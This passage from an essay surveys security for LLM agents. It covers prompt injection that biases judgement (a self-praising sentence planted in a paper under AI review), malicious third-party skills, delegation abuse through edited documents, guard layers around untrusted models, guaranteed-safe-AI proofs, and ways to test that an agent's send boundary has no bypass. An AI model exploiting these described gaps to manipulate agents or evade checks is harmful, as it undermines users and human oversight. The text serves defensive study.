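Santos-Grueiro tested the design on 400 coding tasks. The agent safely completed 231, and he observed no unauthorised action getting past the check. Refusing to act also counts as secure, so the 169 tasks the agent did not safely complete matter when judging that result.

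The design limits a stranger's influence but doesn't remove it. Whoever writes the log can still steer the agent towards any file the path check accepts, and an authorised change can still be a bad one. Similarly, if the owner lets strangers propose meeting times but not choose the other guests, a stranger could still fill the owner's calendar with pointless meetings. How tightly the guarantee limits strangers depends on which decisions the owner is willing to let them make.

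### Misleading text and goals without a rule

An attacker can also do harm without causing any tool call. *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* (Qu, Xu and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that reviews scientific papers. An author adds a sentence to a paper claiming that leading experts consider it the best in its field, and the agent gives it a better review. A check on tool calls has nothing to block, because the sentence contains no instruction and the agent was supposed to read the paper and give an opinion.

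FIDES normally treats a reply to the user as harmless. Costa and colleagues note that a developer could also apply policies to replies, but a strict rule against untrusted replies would stop the assistant from summarising strangers' emails. A label could warn the user that a summary draws on untrusted text, but it would not show which part is wrong.

Qu and colleagues define the missing property as follows. Let q be the user's request, d the material the agent has to read, and J(q, d) the agent's decision. Let δ be an addition to the material that should not change the correct answer. The agent has "Judgment Integrity" if, for every such δ,

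J(q, d ⊕ δ) = J(q, d).

This definition compares decisions on different inputs, so Schneider's limit applies and a monitor cannot establish from one run that an agent meets it. Labels do not help much either, because the decision is supposed to depend on the untrusted material. Testers can run the agent with and without an added sentence and compare the answers, but they cannot try every possible sentence.

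It can also be unclear which additions should make no difference. Self-praise in a paper clearly should make none, but a false report that a camera broke after a week is a harder case, because a careful reader with no reason to doubt it would reasonably think less of the camera.

Other goals can't be stated as precise rules, even when there is no attacker. A developer can specify that the email assistant must never send private files to outsiders, but not what makes a reply tactful or a summary useful. A type can exclude certain operations without defining a good result. Odersky and colleagues chose types for TACIT partly because full specifications of an agent's behaviour are often unavailable or impractical.

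### Four properties for a secure agent

Qu and colleagues argue that agent security lacks an overall definition, and they borrow one from compilers. A correct compiler produces a program that behaves as its source code prescribes. A secure agent, they propose, should turn a user's request into actions that faithfully reflect what the user wanted. They call this "intent-to-execution integrity" and divide it into four properties:

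| Property | What it requires | What current techniques offer |
|---|---|---|
| Instruction Integrity | Every action traces back to an authenticated user's instruction | Strong protection if the agent plans without reading untrusted text, at a cost in useful work |
| Data Flow Integrity | Data in tool calls obeys rules about where it came from and where it may go | Strong protection if somebody writes policies for every tool |
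| Judgment Integrity | Irrelevant additions to untrusted text do not change decisions | No guarantee, though training and filters help |
| Tool Integrity | Each tool does only what it declares | Partial protection from code analysis and sandboxes |

Qu and colleagues added Tool Integrity because many agents now run tools written by strangers. OpenClaw, an open-source assistant, lets users install "skills" from a public collection. They cite one campaign that planted more than 1,000 malicious skills there and an audit that found at least one vulnerability in 26.1 per cent of 42,447 agent skills. A skill that secretly copies passwords does harm even if the agent had good reason to run it.

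To argue that the four properties are enough, Qu and colleagues go through everything an agent does. At each step, it reasons, builds a tool call or runs a tool. Judgment Integrity prevents an attacker from distorting the reasoning. Instruction Integrity prevents an attacker from causing the wrong call, and Data Flow Integrity prevents an attacker from putting the wrong data in it. Tool Integrity rules out misbehaviour by the tool itself. Qu and colleagues compared eleven defences with this list and found that none fully covered it.

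The general conclusion holds up, but the details are less reliable. CaMeL is rated as provably enforcing both Instruction Integrity and Data Flow Integrity, but *The LLMbda Calculus* contradicts the Data Flow Integrity rating with an example in which a private balance leaks through an untaken branch. It also reports that CaMeL's developers described formalisation as a "crucial direction" for future work.

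An agent can also satisfy all four properties without doing what the user wanted. Suppose there is no attacker, and an agent misreads a request and pays Anna instead of Ann. The payment traces back to the user's instruction, its data came from permitted sources, no stranger influenced the decision and the payment tool worked as declared. The properties cover only corruption by an attacker, which is a narrower guarantee than the comparison with a correct compiler suggests. A request in English also often has several possible meanings, unlike source code, which has an exact one.

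Delegation is another weak point. Instruction Integrity lets a user tell an agent to follow instructions in a document. An attacker who can edit the document may then act within the user's permission. The forged bill that defeated the LLMbda agent worked in much the same way.

Qu and colleagues anticipate the objection that their standard is too demanding. They reply that formal verification also set goals for whole programs long before its techniques could handle large ones. As a set of long-term goals, their list is useful for finding gaps in current systems. For example, FIDES and Progent both assume honest tools, and no system in the first table guarantees sound judgement.

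### Assuring the system around the model

Robin Bloomfield and John Rushby, who work on safety-critical computing, think engineers should stop trying to make the model itself trustworthy. In *AI Assurance Needs a Systems Engineering Approach* (2025), they argue for the safe use of AI instead of "safe AI". Their longer report, *Assurance of AI Systems From a Dependability Perspective* (2024), explains why. The most critical systems typically have to fail less than once in a billion demands, and testing alone cannot establish such a low rate. Engineers normally get the remaining confidence from a detailed understanding of how the system works. They cannot understand a trained model that well, so Bloomfield and Rushby recommend treating it as an untrusted component and surrounding it with guards.

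The main objection is that a guard may need AI too. A program that stops a self-driving car from hitting other vehicles first has to recognise them. Bloomfield and Rushby accept this and propose several layers of guards, each either simpler than the one it checks or built differently, ending with conventional software that engineers can fully assure.

How much the layers help depends on whether they fail together. If two guards each miss one hazard in 100 and their failures are independent, one hazard in 10,000 gets past both. If they miss the same hazards, the second adds nothing. Sion and April (2026), in *Who Verifies the Builder?*, cite a classic experiment in which programs written independently by different people tended to fail together. In their own study, AI models tested three small software services containing 46 planted faults. A model working in a fresh context found more of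 the faults than the tests written by the model that had built the software. Using a model from a different company did not improve the result further. This was a small study of software testing, but it suggests that using a second company's model may not make a guard independent.

The objection is weaker for an email assistant than for a car, because a tool call specifies the recipient and the attachment in a form that ordinary software can read, so the guard needs no perception. The objection is stronger when the guard has to evaluate the message's content. For general-purpose agents, Bloomfield and Rushby concede that correctness is hard to specify or check, and they put more weight on recovering from failures. They add that recovery is not a suitable main strategy where harm would be irreversible.

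### Proofs about effects in the world

"Guaranteed safe AI" aims for a much broader guarantee. Dalrymple and colleagues (2024), in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, define it by three components:

- a world model, which predicts the consequences of an AI system's actions
- a safety specification, which states which consequences are acceptable
- a verifier, which shows that the system meets the specification according to the world model

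For an AI system that controls a power grid, the world model would describe how electricity flows and how equipment fails. The specification might require the chance of a blackout to stay below a limit ε. A proof would then cover what happens to the grid, whereas an interface contract might cover only which commands the controller can send. *Toward High-Assurance AI* similarly distinguishes claims about a bounded property from claims about safety in the real world.

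Bloomfield and Rushby call such proposals speculative. The most serious difficulty is that a proof about a model of the world applies to the world only as far as the model is accurate. Suppose the model's probability for any event differs from the true probability by at most η. Then the most that the proof can establish is

true risk ≤ ε + η.

If ε is one in a billion and η is 1 per cent, the proven limit on the real risk is still about 1 per cent. Better proofs can reduce ε, but reducing η requires evidence about the world. *Towards Safe World Models* (Yu, 2026), a survey of 163 works, adds that even a model that predicts well may not be safe to rely on. Errors can also enter through faulty observations, planning or execution, and persist when the system updates its model.

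Supporters reply that engineers can measure and manage these errors. *Foundation World Models for Agents that Learn, Verify, and Adapt Reliably* (2026) proposes that agents learn models which software can formally analyse, and cites earlier methods for measuring how far a simplified model departs from its original. Ammann, in *Safeguarded AI*, a research plan from May 2026, suggests checking observations against the world model while the system runs. A backup controller could take over if they disagree. This would reduce the danger of a wrong model, provided the disagreement appeared in time to act.

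Ammann directs the largest effort described here, a programme at the UK's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA) that runs until the end of 2027. It originally aimed to show that advanced AI could work in critical industries under mathematical guarantees, and so build agreement that powerful AI should operate only behind verified "gatekeepers". In November 2025 it cancelled the part on specialised AI models. Dalrymple, then its director, explained in ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025) that general models were improving faster than he had expected and would probably gain the necessary skills anyway.

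The programme moved £18 million from that work to tools that let AI agents write and check proofs. It now considers timely international agreement on gatekeepers less likely. Its first applications are in cybersecurity, and one candidate is a formally verified firewall for infrastructure such as power grids and water systems. A firewall is an interface, and its behaviour is far easier to specify than an AI system's effects on society. So in 2026 the best-developed part of the research is close to assurance by construction, while proofs about AI's wider effects remain a long-term goal.

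AI could greatly reduce the work of writing such proofs, since a small trusted program can check a proof regardless of who or what wrote it. People would still have to review each proof's assumptions and the specification of what it must show. Ammann expects trust to concentrate in those specifications and assumptions as the proofs grow.

### Testing the boundary itself

A proof or a contract does not show that engineers installed the boundary correctly. Sion and April use a standard formula to separate the possible failures. Let R be what people want, S the written specification, W the assumptions about the surroundings and P the program. A correct system needs

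S ∧ W ⊨ R and P ⊨ S,

where ⊨ means "guarantees". In the email assistant, R might be that outsiders never receive the salary list. S requires the send function to reject marked messages, and W includes the assumption that every message goes through that function. Four gaps can then appear:

| Gap | Example | Remedy |
|---|---|---|
| Between the wish and the specification | The owner also wanted to hide the list from colleagues | People review the specification |
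| Between the specification and the program | A bug lets marked attachments through | Engineers verify or test the program |
| Between the specification and the tests | The tests cover messages but no attachments | Somebody else writes tests that the builder has not seen |
| Between the assumptions and the real surroundings | A new calendar tool sends invitations without using the send function | Engineers collect evidence from the running system |

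A false assumption about the surroundings could be especially dangerous in a test of a model's hacking skills. If the testers believed the model was in a simulation but a misconfiguration had left it connected to the internet, the model could attack real systems.

The decision rule is often the easy part to test. Suppose the send function rejects a message only if the conversation is untrusted and some recipient isn't allowed to read the contents. A tester can try all four combinations of those two conditions and check that only one leads to a refusal.

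It is harder to show that every real message is checked against the rule. Schneider warns that a system may have many ways to send a message, some deeply buried, and that a policy against sending must cover them all. Testers should therefore work inside the deployed system with the agent's own permissions. They can plant a harmless marked file and try to send it out of the system by email, calendar invitation, web request and direct network connection. They should also check that legitimate messages still get through.

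Testers also need to know that their tests would fail if the boundary were broken. In mutation testing, they deliberately damage a copy of the program, for instance by removing the label from a file or deleting the check on recipients, and run the tests again. If every test still passes, none of them was checking that part of the boundary. Under Sion and April's sample requirements for a document service, the tests must detect every such change to the service's authorization checks.

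Engineers need to repeat these tests whenever somebody adds a tool or changes a network setting, since either can make an old assumption false without altering the code that enforces the contract. They can also compare the network's record of outgoing traffic with the send function's log. Any message that appears only in the network's record bypassed the check.
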